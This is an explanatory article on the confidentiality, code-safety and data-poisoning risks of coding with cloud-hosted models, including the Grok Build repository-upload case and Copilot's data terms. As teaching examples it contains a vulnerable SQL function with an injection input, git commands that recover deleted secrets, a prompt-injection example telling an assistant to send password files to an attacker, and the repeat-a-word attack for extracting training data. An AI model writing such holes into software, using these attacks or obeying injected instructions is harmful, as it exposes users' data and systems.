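# Risks of running code written by cloud-hosted language models: confidentiality, unsafe code and data poisoning

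## How code and data travel between a user and a cloud-hosted model

A large language model produces text by predicting what comes next, and because computer code is text, it can also write software. Most people use the leading models over the internet. These models are *cloud-hosted*, meaning that they run on servers belonging to a provider such as OpenAI, Anthropic or Google, so every request leaves the user's machine. Programmers have adopted these models quickly. *Generative AI in Software Development*, a June 2026 report by eu-LISA, the EU agency that runs large IT systems for borders and justice, cites a survey of close to 50,000 developers in which over 80% used AI tools in their work.

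Running code from a cloud-hosted model involves three flows of data. The user sends the provider an instruction, along with any accompanying files, command output and earlier messages. The provider sends back code, which the user's machine runs. Training data, most of it public text and code but some of it from users, goes into the model long before this exchange and sometimes after it. Secrets can leak through what the user sends, the returned code can be unsafe, and anyone who can add to the training data may be able to change what the model writes for other users.

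### One request, step by step

Suppose an employee asks a coding agent for a script that reads the company's customer database and lists everyone who has not ordered for a year. A coding agent is a program that lets a model read files, write code and run commands over many steps. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, handles such a request.

The agent runs on the employee's laptop, while the model runs on the provider's servers. The agent therefore sends the provider the employee's request, along with some standing instructions, a list of the tools that the model may call and a note of the current folder. Little of value has left the company so far. But the model has no details of the database yet, so its first reply is likely to be a command for the agent to run, such as one that prints the configuration file. The agent runs the command,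 appends the output to the earlier text and sends everything back. If the configuration file contains the database password, the provider's servers have now received it, although nobody pasted it anywhere.

The model next requests a sample of the customer table to get the column names right. Codex adds the five returned rows, which contain five customers' names and addresses, to the context too. It includes the history in each new request, or a compressed version when the history grows too long, so the five rows can be sent repeatedly until the task is done.

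Instructions hidden in material that the agent reads can also steer it, which is called prompt injection. For instance, somebody might have hidden a line addressed to AI tools in an outside supplier's documentation that is stored in the project folder. The model receives that line in the same context as the employee's request and may act on both. CodeRefinery's *Security Considerations*, a lesson on programming with AI, gives the example of a comment in a downloaded repository that instructs the assistant to write a script sending all the project's settings and password files to an attacker's site.

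The script that comes back may call for a software library that the model made up, known as a *hallucinated package*. If an attacker has registered that name, installing the package puts the attacker's code on the laptop. The script may also contain a flaw that outsiders can exploit later. The agent may run the script to test it, and if a line deletes rows where it should only read them, the customer records are deleted during the test. A sandbox (an isolated environment that limits which files, networks and credentials running code can reach) is meant to prevent this, but its coverage needs checking. Bolin notes that the Codex sandbox applies only to the agent's own command-line tool. Tools that a user connects from elsewhere, which could well include the one that accesses the database, have to enforce their own limits.

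The provider may keep the exchange after the employee closes the laptop. Depending on the account, it may also use the exchange for training, and a later model might then reproduce a passage from it (this is *memorisation*). The current model's training is also a risk, because the model learned to write database code from examples that strangers had published. If any of those strangers meant harm, the damage was done before the employee used the model.

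### Sending, storing and training

Discussions of privacy often conflate three questions: whether the data left the user's machine, how long the provider keeps it, and whether the provider trains on it. The answer to one doesn't determine the others. For example, a provider can store the data from a request without training on it.

A cloud-hosted model can work only on text that is sent to it. Anthropic's *Data usage*, the policy page for its agent Claude Code, states that data is encrypted on the way to the server. This protects the text from eavesdroppers on the network, but the provider can still read it, because it needs readable text to produce an answer. According to the same page, Anthropic keeps commercial customers' data for 30 days as standard but does not train on it unless they choose to provide it for that purpose. A provider that does not train on a customer's code may therefore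 still store it. Some customers can get zero data retention, a promise not to store requests and replies after processing, but Anthropic's *API and data retention* lists Claude Fable 5.2 among the models that require 30 days' storage unless Anthropic expressly authorises otherwise. By default, Claude Code also keeps a plain-text transcript of each session on the user's own disk for 30 days.

Limiting what the server stores can increase the amount of data sent to it. Bolin explains that Codex resends the conversation history, although it could instead refer back to an earlier reply on OpenAI's servers. It does not do so partly because the server would have to keep the data, so customers with zero data retention could not use the feature.

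When a user does permit training, Anthropic includes the entire related conversation in the training data. It excludes raw content from connected services such as Google Drive, but may include text that the user copies from them into the chat. In the customer example, the conversation would presumably include the five rows, since the agent put them there as command output.

### Snippets, autocomplete and agents

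How much code and data leaves the user's machine depends heavily on the tool. Someone who pastes a function into a web chat chooses what to send and can remove a password first. In a code editor's chat panel, however, GitHub Copilot, one of the most widely used assistants, combines the typed question with open files or repository data before sending it.

As the programmer types, Copilot's autocomplete automatically sends the code around the cursor and snippets from other open tabs, according to GitHub's *Application card* for the feature. Microsoft's *GitHub Copilot user prompt process flow* also lists file names, file paths and information on the project's structure among the data sent. A request can therefore include text from an unrelated settings file that is open in another tab. The suggestion that comes back enters the file only if the programmer accepts it.

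Agents send far more text to the model than coding conversations do. Bai, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *How Do AI Agents Spend Your Money?*, ran eight models through an agent called OpenHands on 500 real software problems and counted tokens, the word fragments in which models process text. The agent tasks used about 1,200 times as many tokens as a coding conversation of several rounds, and input accounted for most of the difference. Exposure does not increase by the same factor, because much of the total is the same context sent repeatedly. The more important change for confidentiality is that the agent picks which files to send, following the model's requests, so the user may not know which ones were sent.

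People also review less of the code when an agent runs it. Someone who uses a chat window has to copy the code and run it themselves, which gives them a chance to read it first. Agents run code themselves, and for a while the safeguard was a prompt asking the user to approve each command. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approved 97% of these prompts. Most of the commands were probably harmless, as the company concedes, so the figure does not by itself prove carelessness, but it suggests that users were not reading the commands carefully. In August 2026, Anthropic replaced approval of each action with an automated check as the default for new sessions on most of its individual and team plans.

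These categories describe ways of working more than products. GitHub Copilot began as autocomplete and now also has an agent mode, so a company that says it "uses Copilot" has not specified how much code and data it sends or who reviews the commands.

### Three causes of a bad script

An accidental flaw, a poisoned model and a prompt injection can all lead to the same dangerous line of code. The cause lies in a different place in each case, but nobody can reliably tell from the line alone which of the three produced it.

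With an accidental flaw there is no attacker. Models learn from public code, and public code is full of mistakes and of habits that were acceptable fifteen years ago; eu-LISA offers both as likely reasons why GitHub Copilot's early suggestions were so often insecure. Data poisoning needs somebody who deliberately places material in the training data in order to change what the trained model does. The change then sits in the model itself and reaches everyone who uses it, though it may stay invisible if the attacker has built in a backdoor, behaviour that appears only when a particular feature is in the input. Prompt injection leaves the model as it was. The hostile instruction sits in a document, and a fresh session without that document is free of it, whereas a fresh session with a poisoned model is not. (The term "tool poisoning", which eu-LISA uses for attacks through compromised external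 tools, is unfortunate here, because such attacks act on the working agent and do not touch the training data.)

A second confusion is between code that is dangerous to run and code that is vulnerable to attack. Dangerous code does immediate damage without any attacker. CodeRefinery's examples include a "cleanup" command that erases the user's home folder. Vulnerable code can run for years and do exactly what its owner wanted, but it has a flaw that causes harm only once an attacker finds and uses it. A sandbox helps against the erasing command, but running vulnerable code in one will usually show only that the code works.

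The classic vulnerability is SQL injection, in which a visitor's input becomes part of a database command. SQL is the language in which programs query databases. Here is a function that the company might use to look up a customer by name:

```python
def find_customer(cursor, name):
    query = f"SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = '{name}'"
    cursor.execute(query)
    return cursor.fetchall()
```

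For "Smith" it returns the customers called Smith. But a visitor to the company's website who types `' OR '1'='1` into the name field closes the quotation mark early and adds a condition that is always true, and the function returns every customer in the table. The safe version keeps the command and the input apart:

```python
def find_customer(cursor, name):
    query = "SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = ?"
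    cursor.execute(query, (name,))
    return cursor.fetchall()
```

Now the database treats whatever the visitor types as a name and nothing else. Both versions pass a test that looks up Smith.

### How researchers count flaws

Researchers label such flaws with numbers from the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a public catalogue that the American non-profit MITRE maintains. Each number refers to a type of software flaw, not to a specific flaw in one program. For example, SQL injection is CWE-89, and operating system command injection is CWE-78.

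Static analysis, which checks code for known flaw patterns without running it, is the low-effort way to look for these mistakes. *SEEK* (2026) measures secure code generation with two collections of test tasks, *CodeGuard+* and *CyberSecEval*, which both grade security this way, using tools such as CodeQL and Semgrep. *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) points out that static analysis matches patterns in the code rather than testing how the program behaves. It also found that many tests in an existing security set inspected the program's text, so a solution could sometimes pass by adding the right comments. Its own tests attack the running program and check what happens.

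Two rates summarise the results. The functional pass rate is the share of tasks in which the generated code does what the task asked. The secure pass rate is the share of *all* tasks in which the code both works and passes the security tests. If a model attempts 100 tasks and produces working code in 80 and working, secure code in 20, the rates are 80% and 20%. Some papers also report security among the working solutions only, which would be 25% here, so readers always need to check the denominator. Security alone is not a useful score because, as Wu and colleagues observe, an attempt that implements nothing passes every security test. *Beyond Pass@k* (2026) points out that functional correctness measures whether code passes its tests, not whether it is safe to deploy.

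### How three public agencies divide the risks

In October 2024 the French and German cybersecurity agencies, ANSSI and BSI, published a joint guide, *AI Coding Assistants* (2024). ANSSI (2024) separately drew particular attention to shared services that users reach over the internet. The guide's list of risks starts with the confidentiality of inputs, followed by *automation bias*, the tendency to trust output because it is fluent, and code of poor quality or security. Next are attacks through the supply chain: hallucinated packages, indirect prompt injection, poisoned data or models, and extensions that act on the programmer's behalf. The last risk is misuse of the tools by attackers.

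The guide also identifies who can reduce each risk. Developers can read the generated code and companies can forbid private accounts, but the agencies give manufacturers, who choose and check the training data, the main responsibility for dealing with poisoning. That seems right, but it leaves users with only the general precautions against bad code and records of which assistant they used, in case a poisoning becomes public. The guide is also dated. It mostly describes a programmer choosing among suggestions in an editor, and covers tools that take actions in only a few lines under "extensions".

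By 2026 eu-LISA had divided the risks into three layers, with a separate one for agents. The *output layer* covers insecure code, including hallucinated packages, and the habit of skipping review. The *input layer* covers the sensitive code and data that users send, which the provider may store or train on. The *agent layer* covers what becomes possible once a model can reach files, a command line and the web: prompt injection, theft of data through the agent's own access, and compromised connections to other systems. Code review and static analysis address the output layer, contract terms and local models address the input layer, and sandboxes address the agent layer.

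The layers fit the customer example well, with two gaps. eu-LISA's summary table of risks omits poisoned training data, which ANSSI and BSI had listed two years earlier. Neither the joint guide nor eu-LISA's report has a separate entry for an agent that deletes the customer table by mistake, with no attacker involved.

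## Grok Build: a coding tool that uploaded whole repositories

The coding agent in the customer example sent the provider only what the model had asked to see. Grok Build, the coding agent of Elon Musk's company xAI, sent a good deal more. The researcher cereblab (2026), in *What xAI's Grok Build CLI Actually Sends to xAI*, recorded the tool's network traffic and found that it uploaded the user's entire project, including files that the model never opened. The analysis appeared on 12 July 2026 and concerns version 0.2.93, running on a Mac with an ordinary consumer login. (xAI now belongs to SpaceX and has also gone by the names SpaceXAI and SpaceXSI.)

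Most programmers keep their code in Git, a program that records successive versions of a project. A project folder managed this way is a *repository*. Git records only the files the programmer has told it to track, and a file called `.gitignore` lists the ones to leave out. The repository keeps every saved version, so a password that somebody saves and later removes is still in the history. Git can also pack a repository and its history into a single file called a *bundle*, and anyone who has the bundle can rebuild both with one command.

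### Opening the encrypted traffic

To read Grok Build's encrypted traffic, cereblab used an *intercepting proxy*, a program that sits between an application and the internet and decrypts, records and re-encrypts each message before passing it on. Applications normally reject such a proxy because it cannot present the certificate that proves the real server's identity, but a computer's owner can set it to trust the proxy's own certificate, as cereblab did. This method fails with some applications because they accept only a certificate fixed in advance, but it worked with Grok Build. The proxy logged each request's destination and size and the server's status code, where 200 means that the server accepted the request. It also saved the contents of requests to xAI.

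To trace the traffic back to particular files, cereblab built a throwaway project with a unique nonsense string in each file. One file imitated the settings files where programmers keep passwords. It held a fake database password and a fake API key, a credential that one program uses to identify itself to another. In some runs, the project also contained a marked file that the prompt told the agent not to open.

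If a marker appears in the traffic, the file containing it has left the machine, because the string exists nowhere else. A file can leave undetected, however, since it may have been compressed, which hides the marker from a text search, or sent over a connection that bypassed the proxy.

### Model requests and the storage channel

When Grok Build read a file, it included the contents in its next request to the model, as Codex does. One such request, 48,070 bytes long, contained both fake secrets unredacted. But the fake secrets were not formatted like real keys, so cereblab could not rule out a filter that redacts real ones.

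Grok Build also copied what it had read into a session archive and uploaded the archive to a separate storage address. The model did not need this second copy to answer.

The same storage address received the whole repository too. The destination was a Google Cloud storage area called `grok-code-session-traces`, according to file names inside the program and in the data it prepared for upload. To see how much the tool would send, cereblab filled a repository with 12 GB of random data, which compression cannot shrink, and started a session. The requests to the model totalled 192 KB. When cereblab stopped the capture, the tool had sent 5.10 GiB to storage, about 27,800 times as much, and was still uploading. It sent most of this in 73 pieces of about 75 MB each, and the server accepted every one.

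Partway through, the account used up its free allowance and the server began refusing requests to the model. The uploads continued, so they did not depend on the model's responses.

The ratio became the best-known number of the affair, but it mostly reflects the size of the repository that cereblab chose, since no task required 12 GB of random data. Axios' *SpaceXAI wipes customer data after Grok uploads sensitive information* describes the 192 KB as what the coding task required, but cereblab did not record the prompt for that session. In another test, on a small but real code project, the entire repository was 152 KB, less than the 192 KB of model traffic in the large test. A small upload can do as much damage as a large one if it contains a company's database password.

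### Why the recovered file is better evidence

The byte count also does not show what was in the uploaded pieces. Gigabytes left a repository that the model had not read, and cereblab saw the volume grow with the size of the repository, from 64 MB up to 12 GB. The obvious explanation is that the pieces contained the repository's files, but cereblab had not managed to unpack them, so this was an inference from their size.

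In the test on the small project, cereblab planted a marked file and told the agent to reply "OK" and open nothing. Grok Build uploaded a Git bundle, and the server accepted it. cereblab then extracted the bundle from the captured request and ran Git's clone command on it. This recovered the repository, with 47 files, four saved versions and the planted file, its marker intact. A second, unrelated project gave the same result. These tests show directly, without inference from upload sizes, that the contents of unread files left the machine. The 12 GB session shows that the uploads were not limited to small projects.

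The model probably did as it was told, while the program around it uploaded the file anyway. In a control run with a similar prompt, cereblab found no trace of the unread file in any request to the model. Some readers concluded that the model had disobeyed its instructions, but The Stochastic Parrot's *Grok Build Uploaded Repos on a No-Read Prompt* (2026), an article from a machine-run news site, correctly points out that the capture does not show what the model did. An instruction such as "do not open the passwords file" is addressed to the model and does not control the rest of the software.

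### The setting that governed something else

Before the bundle test, cereblab had switched off "Improve the model", the privacy setting that most users would have tried first. This didn't stop the upload, because that setting only controls whether xAI may train on the data. Uploading depended on a separate setting that xAI's servers sent to the program, which was still `trace_upload_enabled: true`. A user who had refused training could easily have believed that their code was staying on their laptop.

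wetlink, a commenter on cereblab's analysis, found that users could block the repository upload by adding the line `disable_codebase_upload = true` to a configuration file, even when other settings forced the upload on. xAI later stated that it had respected the choice of users who disabled uploads. That may well be true of users who had added this line, and it does not contradict cereblab's result, which concerned a different switch.

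Few users had reason to suspect the repository upload. cereblab found no description of it in the installation script or the quick-start guide, but did not search all of xAI's documentation. According to The Next Web's *Grok Build was uploading entire Git repositories to xAI's cloud*, xAI had marketed the tool with the claim that "nothing from your codebase" reached its servers during a session. That claim would have been false even without the repository upload, because the tool's requests to the model also contained material from the codebase.

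### What the captures leave open

The captures show that the data left the machine and that xAI's server accepted it for storage, but not that xAI trained on the code or that anyone at the company looked at it.

It is also unclear what happened to files that Git had been told to ignore, where careful programmers keep their passwords. The Hacker News reports that an ignored file stayed out of the bundle if it had never been committed (saved into the history). Git bundles do work that way, but cereblab did not test the case, and the program also contained code for packing the workspace in another format. Two reports suggest that the tool uploaded more than this. Willison (2026), in *xai-org/grok-build, now open source*, quotes a user who ran the tool in their home folder and said that it uploaded their password manager's database, their photos and "everything". wetlink's own log listed 339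 queued repository uploads, including a session that covered a whole home folder. Home folders are seldom Git repositories, so if these reports are right, the tool could also upload untracked files. But the first report rests on one user's word, and the uploads queued in wetlink's log may not have finished.

cereblab had to retract one claim, and the mistake is useful to anyone planning a similar audit. The first conclusion was that the large uploads failed and that the program then deleted them locally, so nothing much had left the machine. This came from a monitor that counted the traffic of a single process and showed less than 1 MB. It missed a separate process that handled uploads, as well as data that went straight to Google's addresses without passing through xAI's. The proxy caught what the monitor had missed. cereblab also stopped treating an emptied upload queue as evidence of anything,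 because the program clears the queue whether an upload succeeds or fails.

### Needed and excess transmission

Every cloud-hosted agent sends some code, so the useful measure is how much it sends beyond what the model needs for the task. Grok Build stood out on this measure. The Hacker News reports that cereblab ran the same kind of test on three rivals and found no repository bundle from Anthropic's Claude Code or OpenAI's Codex. Google's Gemini tool sent none while idle, but a usage limit cut off its test on a realistic task. In October, The Stochastic Parrot repeated the idle test on all three rivals, with three runs each, and found neither markers nor bundles. These results are reassuring but limited, because the October test used only one prompt and one machine, and not finding markers is weaker evidence than finding them.

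A coding tool can have a good reason to send more code than a task needs. Arize's *Is your coding agent uploading all your code?* compares the documentation of five coding agents and finds that Cursor, a popular code editor, also sends extra code when a user turns on indexing. It uploads the project in pieces to build a search index, then discards the readable text. Cursor documents this, and the purpose is clear. Gergely's *Grok's CLI caught uploading all your local files to the cloud* describes a more private process, in which the index is computed on the user's own machine. Under either description, Cursor's indexing is better than copying everything without telling the user, as Grok Build did.

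Musk said that retaining some data helps with debugging. Gergely replies that neither the history nor the password files are useful for that. A snapshot of the code might help an engineer reproduce a failed session, but it is hard to see what years of old versions would add. xAI switched the uploads off without withdrawing the tool, which suggests that the tool never needed them to write code.

### The company's response

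The uploads stopped on 13 July, the day after publication, without an update to the program. cereblab retested the same version, 0.2.93, six times and saw no storage requests. xAI's servers now returned `disable_codebase_upload: true`, and The Hacker News reports that a second developer saw the same on his account. Because xAI made the change on its servers, it protected users without requiring them to install an update. A later version, 0.2.99, still contained the upload code, so xAI could have turned uploads back on without releasing an update.

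xAI publicly directed users to the `/privacy` command, which it said would disable retention and delete data already collected. cereblab tested the command. According to Arize, it changed only one retention setting on the account, and session archives still uploaded in full. cereblab wrote that it "does not change what leaves your machine". This is hard to reconcile with the six retests in which nothing went to storage, unless the tests ran under different server settings. Still, both results indicate that the server switch, not `/privacy`, stopped the repository uploads.

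xAI also said that it had never retained code from teams with zero data retention. cereblab tested only consumer accounts, so the captures neither support nor undermine this.

Musk promised on 13 July that all data uploaded until then would be "completely and utterly deleted". Two days later xAI acknowledged that retention had been on by default for other users during the early beta, and said it had ended this on 12 July. It also published the program's source code that day. Willison found remnants of the upload code there, including a function for uploading session archives that now only returned an error. xAI released a single version without the code's history, so outsiders could not see when or why the upload feature had been added.

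CyberInsider's *SpaceXAI admits Grok retained developer data in open source announcement* lists what xAI had still not disclosed, including how many users the uploads affected, how long it had kept the data and whether it would notify anyone.

xAI documented Grok Build's privacy controls later. *xAI Docs* (2026), Tech Dev Notes' log of changes to xAI's manuals, dates the section on them to 28 July. The October version of SpaceXSI's *Security* describes a screen that asks users to let the company retain data to improve the product and the model.

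Grok Build has continued to upload some data. Tech Dev Notes' *Grok Build 1.0.20* (2026) describes a September release in which one-off automated runs allow at least 150 seconds for "trace uploads" to finish before exiting. The release notes do not specify what a trace contains, so the July finding that Grok Build had stopped uploading whole repositories does not establish what this version sends. Dent's *A Grok vibe-coding agent leaked sensitive SpaceXSI data* (2026) reports that in November a separate flaw in Grok Build leaked data from thousands of users, including xAI itself.

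### What users could check, and why they had to replace their passwords

A user with some technical skill could repeat cereblab's test to see what a given version sent from their own machine. Since mid-July they have also been able to read the source code and build the program from it, so that they know they are running the code they read. Both checks go out of date with the next update, or sooner if a setting changes on the server.

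Outsiders could check almost nothing beyond the user's machine. The Next Web notes that no independent audit has confirmed the deletion. Nobody outside xAI could establish whether backups existed or who had opened the files before they were deleted. Relying on xAI's confirmations also requires trusting xAI. For example, its API labels each reply to show whether zero data retention is on. The label can help customers notice that someone forgot to enable the setting, but they cannot use it to verify what the server does with the data.

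A user can do little more than accept that uncertainty for source code, but can replace exposed passwords and keys so that any surviving copies no longer work. Even if xAI deletes its copy as promised, anyone who had already read or copied a password or key could go on using it until it is replaced.

The owner has to look further than the current files. Suppose that the company in the customer example had once saved its database password in a file called `settings.env` and later removed it. Anyone with the uploaded bundle could recover it like this:

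```
git clone uploaded_repo.bundle recovered
cd recovered
git log -p -- settings.env
```

The first command rebuilds the repository, and the last prints the recorded changes to the settings file, including deleted lines. The Hacker News therefore advises replacing every credential that appears in a tracked file, in the history, or in a file the agent read. The company would have to change the password on the database itself, because deleting it from the code would leave the old one working.

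## GitHub Copilot: what providers keep and train on

xAI collected users' repositories without telling them, whereas GitHub gave a month's notice before it began training on its users' data. In March 2026 the company announced that from 24 April it would train AI models on data from Copilot Free, Pro and Pro+, its plans for individuals, unless users opted out. It exempted Copilot Business and Copilot Enterprise, the plans for organisations.

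### What GitHub collects, and why

GitHub calls the material *interaction data* and says it includes what users send to Copilot, the code around the cursor, the suggestions they accept or change, and their comments, file names and ratings. In the customer example, a developer on a Pro plan who had Copilot write the database script would supply the script as interaction data, along with the configuration file and the five customer rows if the agent had read them.

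GitHub says it doesn't train on private repositories "at rest", meaning the copies stored on its servers. But Copilot processes private code whenever the owner uses it in the repository, and GitHub may train on what Copilot processes. TechSpot doubts that many developers will find this distinction comforting. The distinction protects files that nobody opens with Copilot, but very little of a project that an agent has read in full.

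GitHub also excludes data from repositories owned by enterprise customers from training. This would not protect a company whose employee copies work code into a personal project. Washington State University's *GitHub Copilot Interaction Data Usage Policy* forbids using personal Copilot plans for university code unless the user has turned off training and obtained written approval.

GitHub bases its case for the change on an earlier trial. It built its first models from public data and hand-written samples, then added interaction data from Microsoft employees. It reports that programmers then accepted more suggestions in several languages, but gives no figures. Acceptance rates also measure how often people keep suggestions, which is a poor guide to whether the code is secure. Interaction data is still probably useful, because public repositories contain finished code and seldom record which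 suggestions programmers rejected while writing it.

Critics objected mainly to the default. *Opt out is not consent* (2026) argues that Microsoft, GitHub's owner, built proper consent for enterprises and chose not to extend it to individuals. The essay adds that GitHub's notification email had no direct link to the setting, and that GitHub's FAQ post drew over 160 thumbs-down reactions. The New Stack's *GitHub will train AI models on your Copilot data* (2026) reports that some users gave GitHub credit for showing a banner. A few hundred reactions are weak evidence about more than 26 million users, but the objection doesn't depend on how many people share it, because someone who never saw the notice has not agreed to anything.

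In late 2024, GitHub was still telling individual subscribers that it would use their prompts to fine-tune its model unless they opted out. This complicates the essay's claim that the change was a reversal because GitHub had once trained on user data and then stopped.

Under the terms in GitHub's *Updates to our Privacy Statement and Terms of Service* (2026), opting out stops GitHub from collecting more data but does not remove what a model has already learned from earlier data. GitHub may share the data with Microsoft, but not with outside model companies for their own training. GitHub told The New Stack that it may keep interaction data for up to five years, but often keeps it for less time.

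### The same question, kept for a moment or for good

The exemption for organisations covers training, but GitHub still stores some of their data, depending on where the employee types. According to *Demystifying GitHub Copilot Security Controls* (jorgebalderas, 2025), a post on Microsoft's developer blog, GitHub does not keep Business and Enterprise customers' prompts from the code editor. It keeps prompts from most other places for 28 days and the coding agent's session logs for the life of the account. Microsoft similarly promises in its contract terms, *GitHub Offerings*, to delete prompts once Copilot has produced a suggestion, with exceptions for command-line tools, customised models and some third-party extensions.

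In August 2026 GitHub (2026) announced that it would keep chats on its website and phone app for the life of the account instead of 28 days, starting no earlier than 28 September. It planned to switch the new version on by default. Cornelißen (2026), in *Copilot-Umbau*, points out that German companies can easily write a 28-day limit into their data deletion plans, but "life of the account" gives them no date to write down. A company that chose Copilot because it deletes prompts may therefore have to limit its staff to using Copilot in the editor.

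### Terms at five providers

The table compares GitHub's terms with those of four competitors. The entries for Cursor and Anthropic's consumer plans are based on Arize's July 2026 reading of the companies' documentation. The Google entries cover its coding assistant, Gemini Code Assist, and the review period comes from its 2025 privacy notice.

| Provider | Trains on individuals' data by default? | Usual retention | What it may keep longer | Terms for businesses |
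|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub Copilot | Yes | Up to five years for interaction data | Agent session logs, for the life of the account | No training; no storage of prompts from the editor |
| OpenAI | Yes, on ChatGPT Free, Plus and Pro | Up to 30 days for API abuse logs | Logs needed for legal or safety reasons | No training by default; zero data retention on approval |
| Anthropic | The user chooses at setup | 30 days, or up to five years with training on | Flagged content for two years, safety scores for seven | No training by default; 30 days' storage |
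| Google | Yes, on the free version | Varies by product | Copies for human reviewers, up to 18 months | No training on Standard and Enterprise |
| Cursor | Yes, with Privacy Mode off | None at its model suppliers in Privacy Mode | Prompts that trigger abuse checks, even in Privacy Mode | Privacy Mode on by default |

GitHub's claim that it follows industry practice is fair for individual plans. In every row, the terms depend on who pays, so the same program can come with different terms. A developer who signs in to Codex with a personal ChatGPT account gets that account's terms, according to OpenAI's *Using Codex with your ChatGPT plan*, while a colleague on the company's account gets the business terms.

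Opt-outs also have exceptions. OpenAI's *How your data is used to improve model performance* says that when a user rates a reply, OpenAI may train on the entire conversation, even if the user has opted out. If a user gives the finished database script a thumbs-up, OpenAI could therefore train on the customer rows from earlier in the session.

### A scorecard for privacy policies

AL-Maamari (2025), in *Can You Trust Your Copilot?*, tried to turn such terms into a ranking. The study covered Amazon Q Developer, Claude, Copilot, Gemini and OpenAI's GPT models, using documents from mid-2025: privacy policies, business contracts, technical manuals and outside evidence such as audit reports. Each assistant received 0, 1 or 2 points on 14 criteria in three groups. A legal expert and a data protection officer decided how much each group should count, which gave the formula

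score = 100 × (0.325 × *governance* + 0.425 × *safeguards* + 0.25 × *transparency*),

where each term is the share of that group's points that the assistant earned. Gemini came first with 89.25, followed by Claude (81.88), Copilot (78.75), Amazon Q (72.38) and the GPT models (68).

The scores are reported more precisely than the method justifies. Raising one of the five criteria on technical safeguards from "partially met" to "fully met" adds 4.25 points. Claude's lead over Copilot is smaller than that, so a single judgement about an ambiguous policy could reverse it. The gap between first and last equals five such changes, which is harder to attribute to one reader's interpretation.

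Two findings matter more than the ranking. Four of the five providers relied on users to keep passwords and personal data out of their prompts, with no automatic filter. Every provider except Anthropic trained on consumer data unless the user opted out, so AL-Maamari recommended Claude to anyone who wanted opt-in consent. That advice went out of date almost at once, because in August 2025 Anthropic began asking consumer users to allow training, with the switch already set to "on".

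A scorecard of documents also has no way to catch a provider whose software does something the documents leave out, as Grok Build did.

### What zero data retention covers

Zero data retention is the strictest promise in the table, but it can have many conditions. OpenAI offers it only to approved customers of its API, the interface through which a company's own programs send requests. OpenAI normally logs API prompts and replies for up to 30 days to look for abuse. For approved customers, it leaves the content out of those logs and overrides any request to store a reply.

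The promise covers ordinary text requests but not uploaded files, saved conversations, batch jobs or OpenAI's hosted agents. OpenAI may keep the contents of these until the customer deletes them. If the company in the customer example uploaded its customer table as a file, OpenAI would store the table, whatever the account settings.

Some data also remains after a request that does qualify. OpenAI may hold encrypted working data from a prompt on its graphics processors for up to 24 hours to answer related requests faster. It also keeps images that its filter flags as possible child sexual abuse material. If the model uses another company's tool, that company's retention terms apply to whatever the tool receives.

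OpenAI can also withdraw zero data retention for a particular model and customer, after written notice, to investigate or prevent severe risks. This exception exists because a provider that keeps no requests cannot detect an attacker who splits a harmful task across many innocent-looking ones. Anthropic therefore requires 30 days' storage for Claude Fable 5.2. OpenAI's *Offering Zero Data Retention for frontier models* (2026) previews another approach, Private Safety Processing, in which automated checks look for patterns across requests held in storage that the customer controls. OpenAI's staff would see the type and severity of an alert but not the text. If this works as described, customers would give up less privacy than under compulsory storage by the provider, but they would have to set up and run the storage themselves.

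### The New York Times order

A court may also stop a provider from deleting data. The New York Times sued OpenAI for copyright infringement in 2023 and wanted evidence of what ChatGPT had written for users. On 13 May 2025, Magistrate Judge Ona Wang ordered OpenAI to preserve output logs that it would otherwise have deleted, including chats that users had asked it to delete. District Judge Sidney Stein rejected OpenAI's objection in June.

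The order applied to ChatGPT's Free, Plus, Pro and Team plans and to ordinary API customers. It did not affect ChatGPT Enterprise, ChatGPT Edu or API customers with zero data retention. OpenAI had no stored text from the zero-retention customers to preserve, which is the best practical argument for zero data retention. A court order overrides a contract that promises deletion after 30 days, and OpenAI's API terms now allow longer storage where the law requires it.

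The general duty to preserve new chats ended on 26 September 2025, under an agreement that Judge Wang approved in October, though OpenAI still had to keep the chats it had already set aside. In November Judge Wang ordered OpenAI to give the plaintiffs a sample of 20 million chats with identifying details removed, and Judge Stein upheld the order in January 2026. Removing names and account details protects code less than small talk, because a company's source code may itself identify the company.

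AL-Maamari calls OpenAI's deletion tools "functionally misleading" because of the order. The phrase seems harsh for a company that fought the order in court, but people who deleted a chat in June 2025 had reason to believe it would be gone within weeks, and it was not.

### From one user's prompt to another user's screen

More specifically, many companies fear that code an employee sends will later appear in an answer to a competitor. This can happen through training only if the provider stores the code and selects it for training, the model memorises it, and someone gets the model to reproduce it.

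The providers' own terms describe how they store data, so storage needs little further evidence. How they select data for training is much harder to observe. GitHub says it filters out sensitive data before training and removes identifying details where it can, but outsiders can't measure how well the filters work. A filter may well recognise a password in a standard format, but it has no obvious way to identify an ordinary-looking pricing function as a trade secret.

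Memorisation depends heavily on repetition. *Deduplicating Training Data Mitigates Privacy Risks in Language Models* (Kandpal, Wallace and Raffel, 2022) found that models reproduced a passage that occurred ten times in the training data about 1,000 times as often as one that occurred once. The risk is therefore lower for a function that one employee pasted once than for code sent by an agent, which sends the same lines again with every request. Unless the provider removes duplicates before training, one long session could add dozens of copies of the same password to the training data.

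In *Traces of Memorisation in Large Language Models for Code*, Al-Kaswan, Izadi and van Deursen (2024) gave an open code model the beginnings of passages from its training data, and it continued 47% of them word for word. They had picked passages that looked extractable, so the figure does not mean that the model had memorised nearly half of its training data. They also found that models memorised files that mainly hold data at a higher rate than ordinary code, which puts settings files and tables of customers at greater risk.

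Researchers have also extracted secrets from commercial assistants. Huang, Li and colleagues (2024), in *Your Code Secret Belongs to Me*, took public files that contained passwords or keys, removed the secrets and asked Copilot to fill the gaps. With 900 such prompts they collected 2,702 strings in a valid format. Copilot had invented most of them. Well under a tenth matched real strings on GitHub, and two of the credentials still worked. Niu, Mirza and colleagues (2023), in *CodexLeaks*, looked for personal information in the output of the model behind Copilot and found leaks for about 8% of their prompts.

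Safety training does not reliably stop a model from reproducing its training data. In *Scalable Extraction of Training Data from (Production) Language Models* (2023), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues asked ChatGPT to repeat a single word forever. It eventually stopped and began to reproduce training data. They report recovering more than 10,000 distinct passages for about $200. OpenAI has since blocked that particular prompt.

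All of these studies recovered text that was public when the models were trained on it. This let the researchers confirm matches. It also made the attack easier, because Huang and colleagues could give Copilot the exact lines around each missing secret. A competitor would not normally have the lines around a company's private password, and would have trouble telling a real password from an invented one. The studies show that code models can memorise and release secrets, but no study recovered code that a customer had submitted.

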